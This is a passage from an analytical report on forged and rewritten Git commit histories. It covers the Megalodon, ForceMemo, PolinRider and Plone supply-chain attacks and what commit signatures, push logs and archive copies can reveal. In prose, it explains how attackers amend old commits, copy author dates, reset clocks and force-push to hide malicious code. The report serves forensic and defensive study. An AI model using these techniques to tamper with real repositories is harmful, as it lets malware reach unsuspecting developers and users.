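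None of this can prove what Cook intended, but an accident is still by far the better explanation, because the rewriting left the code itself unchanged and other people had run into the same fault. Cook was careless, though. He overrode his scripts for checking work before a push, and Corbet reports that he force-pushed the result. In a comment under Corbet's article, Cook said he had since added stricter checks, including one on the point where his branch meets Torvalds's.

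Disabling the account was a defensible precaution, because an intruder with Cook's credentials could have done more harm the longer they had access. Ryabitsev could easily restore the account, but the accusation of malice was harder to take back. Corbet describes how the news spread online with speculation about an attack on the kernel's supply chain, while Cook could not use the account he needed to repair the damage. It's FOSS, a Linux news site, reported that Cook had submitted 330 pull requests copying Torvalds's patches. He had sent one request, and the 330 were merge commits inside the branch. Torvalds accepted a corrected request on 1 June, and Cook's *hardening fixes for v7.2-rc6* (2026) shows that he was still sending Torvalds pull requests in July 2026.

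Once Torvalds knew the cause, he was angry at the tool instead. He wrote that it is normal to put somebody else in the author field, because that field gives credit, but that doing so in the committer field is "lying" and a tool that does it is broken. He asked Ryabitsev to stop b4 from ever rewriting another person's commits. Ryabitsev agreed to add the check but pointed out that git-filter-repo was "working as designed".

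Both men had a point. Kernel developers expect the committer field to be true, and Git's everyday commands normally keep it accurate, but Git does not enforce it. Torvalds trusted the convention enough to treat a false name as a sign of bad faith. People who trust the field may believe a forged name, but a less obvious risk is that they may mistake an accidental error for deliberate deception and look for a culprit.

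### Invented robots in the Megalodon campaign

On 18 May 2026 an attacker pushed 5,718 malicious commits to 5,561 GitHub repositories in about six hours. The security company SafeDep found the campaign, known as Megalodon, and The Hacker News (2026) reported SafeDep's figures. The commits' author fields contained the name build-bot, auto-ci, ci-bot or pipeline-bot.

"CI" stands for continuous integration, which means building and testing software automatically whenever the code changes. Many projects let automated accounts commit small maintenance changes, and their developers get used to skimming past them. The attacker imitated these commits with messages such as "ci: add build optimization step", according to StepSecurity (2026), another security company. The PHP attacker had used the names of known maintainers, who could deny having made the change, but nobody could do that for "build-bot".

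The commits added or replaced workflow files, which contain commands that GitHub's machines run automatically for a project. The new commands collected any passwords, keys and access tokens the machine could reach and sent them to the attacker's server. One version ran on every push and pull request (a proposal to merge a change), while the other ran only when the attacker started it.

According to SafeDep, quoted in Kowatek's *Megalodon GitHub Attack Targets 5,561 Repos with Malicious CI/CD Workflows* (2026), the attacker created throwaway GitHub accounts with random eight-character names, set the false author in Git's configuration, and pushed with stolen access tokens or deploy keys (keys that give a machine access to a repository). The bots named as authors therefore existed only in the text of the commits.

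OX Security's *Megalodon* instead reports that the attacker sent pull requests and that the malware ran once a repository's owner merged them. StepSecurity agrees with SafeDep that the attacker pushed directly to branches that did not require a review. Direct pushes fit the timing better, because thousands of owners are unlikely to have merged similar changes within six hours.

SafeDep's investigation began with Tiledesk, a chat platform whose developers publish a package on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript code. Several versions released between 19 and 21 May contained the malware, while the previous one, 2.18.5, was clean. SecurityWeek's *Over 5,500 GitHub Repositories Infected in ‘Megalodon’ Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports that the same npm account published both the clean and the infected versions. According to SafeDep, the account's owner was neither guilty nor hacked,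 though the publishing record could have suggested either. The attacker had changed the project's GitHub repository, and the maintainer had published from it without noticing.

SafeDep traced the infected releases to a commit by "build-bot". It searched for the email address in the commit's author field and found 2,878 commits from the same day, then found 2,841 more under a second address. A search for Lerdorf's address would have returned years of genuine work, but these addresses were invented, so the search found more of the same attacker's commits. It did not reveal who the attacker was.

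OX Security found that the commits also carried a fixed, false date of 17 September 2001, more than three years before Git existed. An owner who searched a repository's history for commits dated May 2026 could have missed the malicious one.

None of the security companies appears to have publicly identified the attacker. OX Security noted a similarity to TeamPCP, a criminal group that had recently broken into GitHub and whose leaked code also set a false commit date, in January 2099. The link is weak because anyone could copy the trick once the code had leaked, and falsifying a date takes little skill.

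A larger campaign in November 2026 used real people's accounts instead. TechRadar's *Thousands of GitHub repositories targeted in widespread attack* reports that attackers opened pull requests in 61,764 repositories from 4,837 compromised accounts. Aikido, the security company that investigated the campaign, published the original report, *wfx-loot campaign pushes CI secret stealer to tens of thousands of repositories*. A repository owner who looked up the account behind one of those requests would have found a real GitHub user who had nothing to do with the attack.

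### What a second copy can and cannot show

In both Linux cases, somebody discovered the false entries by comparing them with a copy that the person or tool responsible had not touched. That copy was BitMover's internal one in 2003 and Torvalds's own repository in 2025. Nothing in the name fields showed that the entries were false.

Torvalds described this protection in 2003, when he explained why the BitKeeper version would have been harder for an intruder to corrupt. The public copies were replicas of the ones developers worked on privately. If a public copy had contained a change he did not have, his next push to it would have failed and he would have noticed. Git's check on ordinary pushes gives a team that works from several copies some of the same protection, even if nobody planned for it.

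A comparison shows that two copies differ, but people still have to work out why. McVoy knew that the public file was wrong but never learned who had changed it. Torvalds could tell that the 330 merge commits were not his, but he blamed the wrong cause. The reflog, the list of typed commands and a test that other people could repeat later showed that he was mistaken.

The method also requires a true version for comparison. The 2003 forger altered a copy whose original was elsewhere, and b4 duplicated commits that already existed. But the Megalodon and PHP attackers added new commits to the main repository. Developers' copies would have received those commits, with their false names, at the next update, and all the copies would then have matched.

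## Can the history be rewritten after the fact?

The PHP and Megalodon attackers added new commits, so anyone who read the log could see an extra entry, even if the name on it was false. An attacker who can force-push can avoid adding an entry by putting the malicious change inside a commit that a real developer made months or years ago, then replacing the original with the altered version.

### How a change ends up in an old commit

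In the invented company described at the start of this report, the last commit before Ines Falk raised the chatbot's blocking threshold was `3fb2...`. Suppose Omar Haddad made that commit on 12 February to correct a spelling mistake in a refusal message. On 3 March, an intruder with a stolen copy of Falk's access token downloads the repository, changes the threshold to 0.97 and runs `git commit --amend`. Developers normally use this command to fix a mistake in a commit they have just made. Git can't edit a finished commit, so it makes a new one that contains both Haddad's correction and the intruder's change, and copies Haddad's name, date and message onto it.

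| Part of the commit | Haddad's original | The intruder's replacement |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Hash | `3fb2...` | `e6a8...` |
| Threshold in the files | 0.80 | 0.97 |
| Author and author date | Omar Haddad, 12 February | Omar Haddad, 12 February |
| Committer and committer date | Omar Haddad, 12 February | Name set on the intruder's machine, 3 March |
| Message | Correct spelling in refusal message | Correct spelling in refusal message |

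The intruder then force-pushes, which moves `main` to `e6a8...`. The replacement takes the place of `3fb2...` in the log, so the number of entries stays the same. By default, `git log` shows the author's name and date but not the committer's. A colleague who uses Git to check when the threshold changed will find the change attributed to Haddad and dated 12 February, in a commit about spelling.

The amend command works only on the latest commit. Other Git commands can alter older ones, but because the hashes are chained, every later commit also gets a new hash, which makes the rewriting easier to notice.

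Haddad's colleagues could still notice the swap, because Git will reject the next ordinary push from any copy that ends at `3fb2...`. But few outside users keep a copy from before a rewrite and update it afterwards, as Rapaport et al. point out. Automated build systems often download a fresh copy every time, so they have nothing to compare it with.

### ForceMemo

On 14 March 2026, StepSecurity announced that an attacker was rewriting the history of hundreds of repositories on GitHub. *ForceMemo* (Sharma, 2026) dates the earliest cases to 8 March and counts more than 240 affected repositories by 13 March.

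The attacker first used malicious extensions for two code editors, VS Code and Cursor, to install GlassWorm, a program that stole GitHub access tokens from developers' machines. With each token, the attacker went through the developer's repositories, added disguised code to the end of a Python file in the latest commit on the main branch, and force-pushed the result. The rewritten commit kept the original message, author and author date. The targets included websites and machine-learning research code. When run, the altered files fetched more malware, probably to steal passwords and cryptocurrency.

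The attacker did not set the committer date, so Git set it to the time of the rewrite. In a repository called `request_validator`, the altered commit had an author date of 24 April 2017 and a committer date of 10 March 2026. In `bottom-up-attention-vqa`, the dates were 1 June 2021 and 13 March 2026. The gap was only 33 days in `GDML`, where the latest genuine commit was from February. On many of the commits, the committer's email address was "null", apparently because of a quirk in the attacker's tool. One developer noticed the attack because "null" was listed as a committer in most of their repositories.

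A gap between the two dates is not suspicious in itself. Routinely amending a commit produces one, and so does turning a contributor's month-old email into a commit. A gap of 33 days would be unremarkable in most projects, but it is hard to think of an innocent reason for reworking a project's last commit nine years later under the same message.

GitHub's public record of events was more useful. For `django-restful-admin`, it shows that the main branch moved from `260ca635...`, a genuine merge, to `17849e1b...`, the altered copy, at 21:58:02 UTC on 10 March. An investigator can compare the two commits to see exactly what the attacker added, and the owner can use the first hash to restore the branch. But the record lists the actor as `amirasaran`, the repository's owner, because the attacker had used that account's credentials, as in the PHP case.

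Sharma writes that the method leaves no trail of commits or pull requests in GitHub's interface. That is true of the list of commits, but an owner who knew to check GitHub's activity page could see the force-pushes.

### When both dates match

The committer date was a clue only because the ForceMemo attacker hadn't bothered to forge it. A group linked to North Korea was more careful. Trend Micro's *Void Dokkaebi Uses Fake Job Interview Lure to Spread Malware* describes how the group poses as recruiters, persuades developers to open an infected project as a job test, and then works from their computers. It uses a short Windows script called `temp_auto_push.bat`:

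1. The script reads the date, time, author name, email address and message of the latest commit.
2. It sets the computer's clock to that date and time.
3. It amends the commit to include the malicious code and skips any checks that the developer has set up to run before a commit.
4. It restores the clock and force-pushes the result.

Both dates then match the original. The group could have done this without changing the clock, because Git lets users set either date directly. Trend Micro calls the altered commit indistinguishable from the original in the history, which is true of its names, dates and message but not of its hash or files.

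On 31 January 2026, the attackers used an automated account belonging to the database company DataStax to push altered commits to 12 repositories in 101 seconds. Investigators had to look beyond the commit history for evidence, according to OpenSourceMalware's *TasksJacker DPRK Attack Compromises GitHub Users Via VS Code Tasks* (2026). GitHub records the time of a repository's latest push, which was months later than the dates on some commits. In `cassandra-quarkus`, the attackers' rewrite changed an old commit but not the page for its pull request. The page listed only the developer's original changes to `pom.xml` files, while the commit also contained two VS Code settings files and the attackers' own script, which they had left behind by accident.

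OpenSourceMalware recommends investigating whenever the push time and the commit dates differ by more than 24 hours. This rule would catch many rewrites like these, but it would also flag anyone who commits on Friday and pushes on Monday.

The same article concludes from the speed of the pushes that AI was driving the attack. This evidence is weak, because an ordinary script can push to 12 repositories in 101 seconds, and the article itself describes a script that the attackers used for pushing. The speed is good evidence that the pushes were automated, but it doesn't show whether AI was involved.

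### Was ForceMemo the first?

StepSecurity's announcement was already wrong when it said of the force-push technique, "No other documented supply chain campaign uses this injection method." The Hacker News repeated the sentence.

Plone, an open-source system for managing websites, had suffered the same kind of attack on 7 January 2026. Plone (2026) announced on 16 January that someone had tried to slip malicious code into three pull requests from a member's account. The project later added that one attempt had succeeded on the main branch of an add-on, `plone.app.mosaic`. On 31 January, its release manager wrote on a public security mailing list that the account belonged to a former contributor who still had permission to write to the code (van Rees, 2026, *Security incident on plone GitHub org with force pushes*). The attackers had planted an access token in the account and waited two months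 before using it.

On the main branch, the attackers had altered a routine commit that updated the version number after a release. It was dated 18 December. They put the malicious code after a long run of spaces, which pushed it off the right edge of the screen, so van Rees at first saw what looked like a change in spacing.

The team found the attempts on pull requests because GitHub adds a note to a pull request when somebody force-pushes to it. The altered commit on the main branch took longer to find. Van Rees spotted it on the repository's branches page, where the hijacked user's picture appeared beside the main branch and the time of the last update didn't match the commit's date. He thought the attackers had used force-pushes because people would have noticed ordinary pushes more easily. No release contained the code.

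Two months before the ForceMemo attack, the Plone attackers did the same thing on a smaller scale. GitHub told the project about malicious pushes to five repositories, all in one organization. StepSecurity could perhaps call this an incident rather than a campaign, but that defense fails against OpenSourceMalware's *PolinRider* (2026), which named a campaign with hundreds of victims about a week before StepSecurity's announcement. According to OpenSourceMalware's *PolinRider DPRK Attack Expands Across GitHub* (2026), that first report counted 675 repositories and had already described `temp_auto_push.bat`, including how it kept the original date and force-pushed.

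The Pl0x case of August 2022 is only a partial precedent. Stephen Lacy, a software engineer, found the same malicious code in thousands of GitHub repositories, apparently committed by many different developers over several years. GitHub established that the repositories were copies of real projects and that nobody had broken into the developers' accounts. Arnica's *Demystifying the Pl0x GitHub Attack* (2026) compares one copy with the original, a development platform called Nanobox. In both, the last commit names Tyler Flint as author and is dated 15:58:15 on 21 October 2019. Flint's real commit changed two files and added four lines, while the one in the copy changed 281 files and added 8,430 lines. GitHub still linked the copy's commit to Flint's profile.

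The person behind Pl0x had therefore amended genuine commits, as the ForceMemo attacker later did, but uploaded them to new repositories instead of replacing anything in the real ones. Someone using an anonymous Twitter account claimed responsibility and said they wanted a reward for reporting a security flaw. Arnica was sceptical, with good reason, because the code sent private data to an outside server.

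Some attackers copy a real project's history. In *How I found 10,000 GitHub repositories distributing Trojan malware*, Orchid (2026) describes finding a copy of their own project with every commit intact and Orchid listed as a contributor. Somebody had added one commit with a link to an infected file. In the two copies Orchid watched, that person deleted the last commit every few hours and pushed it again, perhaps to make the project look active.

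PolinRider, or a very similar attack, reached Plone's volunteers in May 2026. Plone (2026) reported that somebody had used a hijacked account to alter about 166 packages in the Plone Collective, a separate GitHub organization for add-ons. One of the altered commits was van Rees's work from December. The security team mostly removed the malicious files with ordinary commits, but in a few cases it force-pushed the original commit back into place. The history of those repositories has therefore been rewritten twice, first by the attacker and then by the security team.

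OpenSourceMalware had confirmed 4,367 PolinRider repositories by July, and The Hacker News' *North Korea-Linked PolinRider Poisons Over 7,600 GitHub Repositories to Spread Malware* (2026) gives a count of more than 7,600 for late November. Nobody knows how many of these have a rewritten history, because the group also spreads its malware in other ways. In March, Trend Micro found the rewriting script in at least 101 of the more than 750 repositories that contained the group's malicious code.

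### How often people rewrite public history

Attackers do only a small part of all history rewriting. The best evidence is from Rapaport and colleagues, who found missing commits in 1.22 million public repositories, or 1.10 percent of those they examined. Their copies came from Software Heritage, an archive that periodically visits public repositories and keeps every copy it takes, even if the owner later changes the history.

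They started from the archive's data for August 2024, left out projects it had visited only once, and compared the rest branch by branch. To avoid counting commits that had changed only through the snowball effect, they looked for the oldest missing commits, which they call root causes. They found 8.72 million and sorted them by what had happened to them.

| What had changed | Root-cause commits | Share |
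| --- | --- | --- |
| Files or directories | 6,693,247 | 76.8% |
| Only the names, dates, message or other metadata | 1,160,725 | 13.3% |
| Only the branch on which the commit appears | 866,113 | 9.9% |

The author field had changed in 667,424 root-cause commits, more than half of those in which only metadata had changed. Developers also change that field when they correct a misspelled name or remove a private email address, so this is not a count of forgeries. The count is also incomplete, because the researchers could match an old commit to its replacement and compare the names only where the files had stayed the same. The ForceMemo attacker kept the author and changed a file. Commits like those would be among the 5.47 million with modified files, alongside routine corrections.

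Much of the rewriting happened where developers expect it. Branches for pull requests accounted for 37.57 percent of all alterations, and branches that a bot called Renovate uses to propose updates accounted for another 9.56 percent. Main branches accounted for 11.39 percent, which is more worrying because other people build on them. That figure is a share of all alterations, not the share of main branches that were altered, although Rapaport and colleagues at one point call it an alteration rate for main branches. Among projects that at least 100 GitHub users had bookmarked, the main-branch share was 1.8 percent.

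Some owners rewrote history for reasons that were neither routine nor malicious. In about 75,000 repositories, people had removed files whose names suggested passwords or private keys. In 32,169 repositories, people had altered license files in the main branch's history. The researchers identified both the old and new licenses in 65,688 of these alterations, and 14 percent of those switched to a different kind of license. The people responsible probably had every right to push to those repositories, but someone who downloads such a project today can't see from its history that it was once available on other terms. An employee could use the same method to hide an embarrassing change to a safeguard.

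The researchers also built a tool, GitHistorian, that lets developers look up a public repository in a database of these alterations. It lists the branch, the commit and the kind of change, and it can run automatically each time a developer downloads updates. Because the database is built from periodic releases of the archive's data, the tool could not have warned anyone about a ForceMemo push on the day it happened. It also does not cover private repositories, where a company would probably keep its safeguard configuration.

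### Force-pushes during review

The archive also misses a rewrite if the original work appeared and disappeared between two visits. Sun, Randrianaina and colleagues (2026) avoided this problem in *Recovering Revisions of Pull Requests with Altered History* by reading the notes that GitHub adds to pull requests after a force-push. They collected 935,011 pull requests opened between February and July 2025 in 1,445 large, active projects. They found 568,218 force-pushes across 242,624 pull requests (26.0 percent) and 1,366 projects (94.5 percent).

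Rapaport and colleagues found altered histories in only 3.3 percent of the repositories with at least 1,000 bookmarks. The two samples differ, but the gap between the results is so large that the archive must be missing a lot of rewriting in busy projects. Rewriting is rare across all public repositories, many of which are barely active, but routine in projects with many contributors.

Most reasons for rewriting history are routine. When a reviewer asks for a correction, the author may amend the original commit instead of adding another. If other people's work has entered the main branch in the meantime, the author may replay the proposed commits on top of it. Both changes require a force-push.

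These routine rewrites can still make a malicious one harder to spot. In 210,837 cases, or 37.1 percent, a plain comparison of the branch before and after the force-push mixed the author's changes with everything that had come in from the main branch. Reviewers may have to read thousands of unrelated lines, and an attacker could hide a few malicious ones among them. Sun and colleagues' program, AntiDiffamine, separated the author's changes from the rest in 98.1 percent of these cases.

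The researchers could not classify another 122,085 force-pushes, because their method needs both the old and the new commit and fails if either one or its branch is no longer on the server. An investigator who has the hash from before a suspicious push can run into the same problem, because the hash alone does not reveal what the old files contained.

A rewritten history is therefore weak evidence of tampering. Even if attackers had rewritten all 7,600 PolinRider repositories, that would equal about 0.6 percent of the 1.22 million in which Rapaport and colleagues found alterations, and their figure is an undercount. The evidence is stronger when a commit on a main branch has kept its author and message but its files have changed, especially if the project had been idle for years. Even a rewrite that looks deliberate can be an accident, as Torvalds found after he accused Cook. An investigator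 still has to compare the files before and after the push, then find out who or what was using the account that made it.

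## Would signed commits have identified the culprit?

If PHP had required signed commits in March 2021, its server would probably have rejected both malicious commits, because the attacker seems to have had two maintainers' passwords but not their private keys. The requirement would not have revealed who the attacker was, because a signature only links a commit to a key, and somebody still has to link that key to a person.

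### What a signature covers

Suppose Ines Falk signs the commit that raises the blocking threshold to 0.97. Git passes the text of the commit, including the names, dates and message, to a signing program, which uses her private key to produce a signature. Git stores the signature in the commit as an extra header and then computes the commit hash. Checking the signature with her public key will fail if any character of the signed text has changed.

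The signed text includes the tree and parent lines, so the signature also covers the value 0.97 and the earlier history. This coverage depends on Git's hash function because, as Courtès (2022) notes, signing a commit amounts to signing a SHA-1 hash.

Signatures make it harder to hide a change in an old commit. An intruder who amended a signed commit by Omar Haddad could copy his name, dates and message, but could not sign the new contents as him without his key.

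Only the committer can sign a commit, so Falk could put Haddad's name in the author field, leave her own in the committer field, and produce a valid signature. GitHub checks the signature against the public keys that users have uploaded, and labels the commit "Verified" if the key and the committer's email address match. *On the Prevalence and Usage of Commit Signing on GitHub* (Sharma and Kancherla, 2025) reports that a commit like Falk's would get that label even if the named author had nothing to do with it. If Haddad had turned on the optional vigilant mode, the label would be "Partially Verified".

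### What a valid signature leaves open

A valid signature proves that somebody used a particular private key to sign this exact commit, but not who did, because people can copy, share or steal keys. In *Claimed or Attested?*, Mockus (2026) examined the signatures in a collection of 5.87 billion public commits. In 32,192 cases, the same key had signed commits under two names that an existing database treated as different people. In 71.9 percent of these cases, the names and email addresses had nothing in common, which Mockus took to mean that two people were sharing a key. Some could be one person using a pseudonym.

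Mockus also picked 398 personal keys at random and looked for them on a public key server. Only 78 were there, and only 39 of those listed the email address used in the commits. An outside investigator who starts with a key often won't find even a claimed owner.

An expiry date on a signing key does little to stop someone who steals the key. In the discussion after Popov announced the PHP attack, Rowan Tommins pointed out that anyone with the private key and its passphrase can change the date.

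An impostor may not need to steal a signing key. Holtgrave and colleagues found 4,107 unregistered internet domains in the email addresses of past contributors to important open-source projects. Anyone could register one of these domains, receive mail at the old contributor's address, confirm the address to GitHub and upload a new signing key. GitHub would then label the impostor's signed commits as verified.

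A signature also doesn't show that the signer was allowed to make the change. Git would accept a signature on the threshold change whether it came from a new intern or the engineer responsible for the classifier.

Signatures also cannot show that commits are missing. If somebody force-pushed `main` back to the commit before Falk's, every remaining signature would still be valid. *Signed git pushes*, a post on the kernel developers' blog, describes a related problem. A developer might sign dangerous experimental code and push it to a branch whose name warns people not to use it. Somebody else could then put the signed commit on another branch, and the signature would not show that the developer never intended this. Git can also sign the push itself, which records the intended branch.

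### The PHP attack under three policies

The effect of signatures on the PHP attack would have depended on what the server did with unsigned commits.

| Policy | What happens to the forged commits | What the maintainers learn |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Signing is optional | The server accepts them | Nothing from the missing signatures, unless the named person always signs |
| Signing is expected but not enforced | The server accepts them | A warning sign, if somebody checks and the named person normally signs |
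| The server rejects unsigned pushes | The server refuses them, unless the attacker has an accepted key | Somebody tried to push without a valid signature |

PHP had the first policy in March 2021. The second would have helped only if Lerdorf and Popov had routinely signed their commits. In that case, the missing signature would have given Popov a reason to doubt the first commit before he read the code. But the back door would still have entered the repository, and he would still have had to find the web server's access log to learn which account had pushed it.

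Under the third policy, the server would have rejected both pushes if the check also covered HTTPS and the attacker could not register a new key with the stolen password. Even then, the maintainers would have known only that someone with a working password had tried to push.

If someone had stolen Lerdorf's signing key, the forged commit would have had a valid signature, and his denial would have been harder to believe.

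Lerdorf tweeted in 2021 that the move to GitHub required signed commits, but PHP was still not enforcing this three years later. In April of that year, Rethans (2024), a PHP developer, asked colleagues whether to require signatures for the main source code. Tommins replied that he had thought this was already the rule, but perhaps nobody had got around to it. Another developer, Jakub, said that most regular developers already signed their commits. PHP had therefore moved from the first policy to something like the second.

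In the same discussion, a developer named Ilija asked what attack the rule would prevent. An intruder who controls a GitHub account can add a new key to it, or make a commit on GitHub's website, which GitHub will sign. If a developer uses one SSH key for both pushing and signing, a thief who copies it can do both. Ilija concluded that the rule mainly stops someone who has stolen the means to push but not a separate signing key. That benefit is narrow, but the 2021 attack appears to have been this kind of theft.

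Tommins answered that compulsory signatures would at least limit a thief to one identity. Without them, anyone with push access can commit under any name, and the project may have to audit every commit. He compared the two cases to stealing one credit card and cloning the card of every customer in a shop. His argument is sound, but PHP is a poor example because the attacker had access to both accounts named on the commits.

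Tim Düsterhus made a better case for signatures as evidence. If a developer suddenly starts signing with a new key, or one commit is signed with a different key from the rest, an investigator has somewhere to start. A developer who keeps a separate key on each computer may be able to tell which machine the intruder used.

GitHub lets a project require signed commits on chosen branches. GitHub's *About required commit signing* warns that this makes contributing harder, and that anyone with an unsigned commit will have to sign it and force-push the result. Ansible, a tool for managing servers, has required signatures in all its GitHub repositories since 16 March 2026. Ansible's *IMPORTANT*, a notice to contributors, gives the commands for re-signing every commit in an open proposal and force-pushing it. A project that introduces the rule should therefore expect many contributors to rewrite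 history for innocent reasons.

### Why a missing signature rarely stands out

A missing signature is useful evidence of forgery only if the person named on the commit nearly always signs. Suppose forgers never sign. If Haddad signs 99 percent of his commits, a forgery is 100 times as likely to lack a signature as one of his real commits (1 divided by 0.01). If he signs only 22 percent, a forgery is about 1.3 times as likely to lack one (1 divided by 0.78), so a missing signature should barely change an investigator's mind.

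Shittu, Sadik and colleagues (2026), in *Analysis of Commit Signing on Github*, studied 16.1 million public commits by 71,694 developers. Among the few who had ever signed a commit made outside GitHub's website, the median developer signed 22 percent of their commits made outside the site. Only 265 people signed all of them, and half of those had made no more than 11 commits.

Four recent studies sampled public commits in different ways, but all found that signing is uncommon. The last column of the table leaves out commits made on GitHub's website, which GitHub signs automatically.

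| Study | Sample | Signed commits, overall | Signed commits, excluding GitHub's website |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Holtgrave and colleagues | 50,328 critical open-source projects | 15.7% | 5.0% |
| Sharma and Kancherla | 60 popular repositories, 2020–2024 | 33.3% | 9.7% (also excluding bots) |
| Shittu and colleagues | 71,694 GitHub developers | 24.1% | 5.2% |
| Mockus | 5.87 billion public commits | 17.6% | Not reported |

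Sharma and Kancherla counted only signatures that GitHub could verify, so their figures would be slightly higher if they had used the other studies' definition. They also compared four fields and found that users had signed 28.35 percent of their commits in security projects but only 2.55 percent in machine-learning projects, including TensorFlow and PyTorch. The share of signed commits rose after GitHub introduced vigilant mode in April 2021, then fell after early 2023 in every field except databases. The researchers could not explain the fall.

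These figures come from public repositories. A company could enforce signing in the private repository that holds its safeguard configuration, and an investigator would need to know whether it did.

Holtgrave and colleagues chose their projects by how many other software packages depended on them. Excluding commits made on GitHub's website, 95.4 percent of the people who had committed to these projects had never signed a commit there, and 2.0 percent had signed all of theirs. In 72.1 percent of the projects nobody had ever signed a commit, and in only 0.2 percent was every commit signed. The researchers described three kinds of impersonation that this leaves open:

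- In contributor spoofing, an attacker puts a trusted person's name on a malicious commit to get it into someone else's project.
- In reputation hijacking, an attacker puts famous developers' names on commits in the attacker's own repository to make it look trustworthy.
- In contribution hijacking, an attacker adds an old contributor's unclaimed email address to a GitHub account. GitHub then credits that person's past work to the attacker, without first checking who owns the address.

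They had records of pushes for only 7,546 repositories. In 6,479 of these (85.9 percent), at least one commit had a pusher who differed from its author or committer, which is often innocent. The summary of their paper therefore overstates what they measured when it says that attackers could abuse the way people contribute to 85.9 percent of the projects.

The paper's count of 573,043 email addresses that attackers could claim also looks too high. Elsewhere, the paper gives the same number as the total of valid addresses in all the commits, and many of those already belonged to GitHub accounts. Its count of about 3 million commits with no linked account better measures how much past work an attacker might try to claim.

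Developers who know about signing also forget to do it. In June 2026 the developers of QGIS, a mapping program, discussed whether to require signed commits. Nyall Dawson had raised the idea, but a colleague pointed out that his own commits appeared to be unsigned. Dawson replied in *Requiring signed commits?* (2026) that he had set up signing once and must have forgotten to do so again after reconfiguring his computer. An investigator who treated his unsigned commits as forgeries would have been wrong.

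When a signature fails GitHub's check, the reason is usually harmless too. Shittu and colleagues found that about one in eight signatures made outside the website failed. In 74 percent of those failures, GitHub had no record of the key.

### Signatures that GitHub makes

When someone edits a file or merges a proposal on GitHub's website, GitHub creates the commit and signs it with its own key, so the user doesn't need one. According to Shittu and colleagues, 82.7 percent of all signed commits came from the website. Among developers with at least one signed commit, 94 percent had never signed anywhere else.

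As a result, a project's developers can appear to sign their commits carefully when they hardly sign any. In Sharma and Kancherla's sample, the database program Redis had 2,784 commits with valid signatures and 312 without. After the researchers removed commits made by bots or on the website, only one of the remaining 312 had a valid signature.

GitHub's signature shows that the commit was made through a session logged in to a particular account. That is better evidence than a name typed into a settings file, but, like PHP's access log, it doesn't identify an intruder who is using someone else's account. Holtgrave and colleagues quote Chacon, the GitHub co-founder, as writing that the company was never very concerned about false names because "you can't push into a repository you don't have access to", but the PHP attacker did have access.

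Mockus found that two platform keys accounted for 95.9 percent of links between authors and signing keys. Only 0.74 percent of the 62.6 million authors in the collection had signed with what appeared to be a personal key. *Scaling Author Identity Disambiguation to the World of Code* (2026) warns against treating everyone who shares a signing key as one person, because platforms, companies' build systems and bots all sign for many people.

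Automatic signatures can give a project a reason to stop requiring personal ones. OpenBao's *signed commits* proposes dropping the signature requirement for most contributors to OpenBao, a program that stores passwords and keys. Its maintainers combine the commits in each proposal into one new commit, which GitHub signs, so the contributors' own signatures add little. Maintainers must still sign their commits.

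GitHub's "Verified" label is also a record of a past check. GitHub's *Persistent commit signature verification now in public preview* (2024) explains that a verified commit keeps its status even if the owner of the signing key later revokes it. This is convenient when a developer retires an old key. But if someone steals a key and signs a commit before the owner discovers the theft, that commit also stays "Verified" after the key is revoked. Investigators need to find out when the key was stolen and examine every commit signed with it since then.

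### The Guix developers' alternative

Courtès works on Guix, a system for installing software whose users download its source code through Git. He objects that GitHub's "Verified" label may show that a key belongs to an account, but not that the project allows the key's owner to make changes. Checking the label also requires trusting GitHub, which signs commits made on its website with its own key and so becomes a single point of trust for every project it hosts.

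Guix keeps the list of authorized keys in the repository itself. The check works as follows:

1. A file called `.guix-authorizations` lists the keys of everyone who may commit.
2. A commit counts as authentic only if its signature comes from a key on the list in its parent commit. A merge has more than one parent, so the key must be on the list in each of them.
3. To add or remove a person, somebody already on the list signs a commit that changes the file. The new list applies from the next commit.
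4. The chain has to start somewhere, so each user also receives the hash of a trusted first commit when installing Guix.

If Falk's company used this method, an intruder could add a new key to her GitHub account and get a "Verified" label, but the commit would fail the company's check. Adding the new key to the authorization file in the same commit would not help, because the check uses the parent commit's version of that file.

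Guix also protects against some force-pushes. Before updating, it checks that the new version descends from the one the user already has, and by default refuses the update if not. This would reveal that someone had replaced or removed commits the user had already downloaded. The check doesn't protect new users, because they have no earlier version to compare.

The method has worked in practice. Between June 2020 and the paper's publication two years later, Guix developers made more than 32,000 commits under the rule. Once, a developer accidentally signed a commit with a key that was not on the list. Anyone who tried to update Guix got an error, and the developers removed the commit within minutes.

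Courtès says the method does not protect against someone who impersonates an authorized developer, for instance with a stolen key. The method also lets every authorized developer change every file. The file format could accommodate separate permissions for each file, which a company would need if it wanted only a few people to be able to change a blocking threshold.

The rule is also awkward for teams that merge proposals on GitHub's website. If a contributor is not on the list, a maintainer has to re-sign the contributor's commits on their own computer, which rewrites the commits. The developers of Nix, a similar system, rejected a proposal for compulsory signing partly because it would have prevented merging through the website. They also regarded GitHub as a trusted third party.

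### XZ Utils and the limits of a known account

Rethans started the 2024 discussion a few days after a back door was discovered in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools used on most Linux systems. A developer named John objected that signatures would not have stopped that attack. The attacker was an active maintainer who had arguably manipulated the original maintainer to gain that position.

The XZ Utils repository recorded the right account. The maintainer, who went by the name Jia Tan, had permission to make changes and could have signed every commit with a valid key. The commits would have passed even the Guix rule if that key had been on the list of authorized keys. But nobody appears to have publicly established who was using the name.

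Düsterhus argued in the PHP discussion that developers' keys would build a reputation through good commits. Jia Tan earned the trust of the XZ Utils project in much this way, by doing useful work for a long time before adding the back door. A key with a good record can show that the same holder probably made both the useful changes and the malicious one, but it cannot show who that holder is or what they will do next.

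## Which records outside the commits can settle the question?

Valid signatures on Jia Tan's commits would have tied them to a key, but not to a known person. Servers, login systems and other people's computers also keep records of a change, and whoever wrote the commit usually can't edit those records. PHP's maintainers, for example, learned from the web server's access log which accounts had pushed the forged commits.

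An investigator can rely on a record outside the commits only if it meets three conditions. It must cover every route by which a change can enter the repository. The gitolite log misled Popov because it left out pushes over HTTPS. The record must also be stored where nobody who can change the repository can alter or delete it. Finally, it must last until somebody thinks to look, which took six weeks in the example of Ines Falk's threshold change.

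| Record | What it shows | Who could alter it | How long it lasts | How it can fail |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Push log | Which account moved a branch, when, and between which commits | Whoever runs the server | As long as the operator chooses | Somebody uses a route that it does not cover |
| Login and network logs | Where a connection came from and how the user logged in | Whoever runs the login system or network | As long as the operator chooses | An intruder works from the account owner's own computer |
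| Independent copy | Which commits and files existed on a given day | Whoever keeps the copy | As long as that person keeps it | A change comes and goes between two copies |
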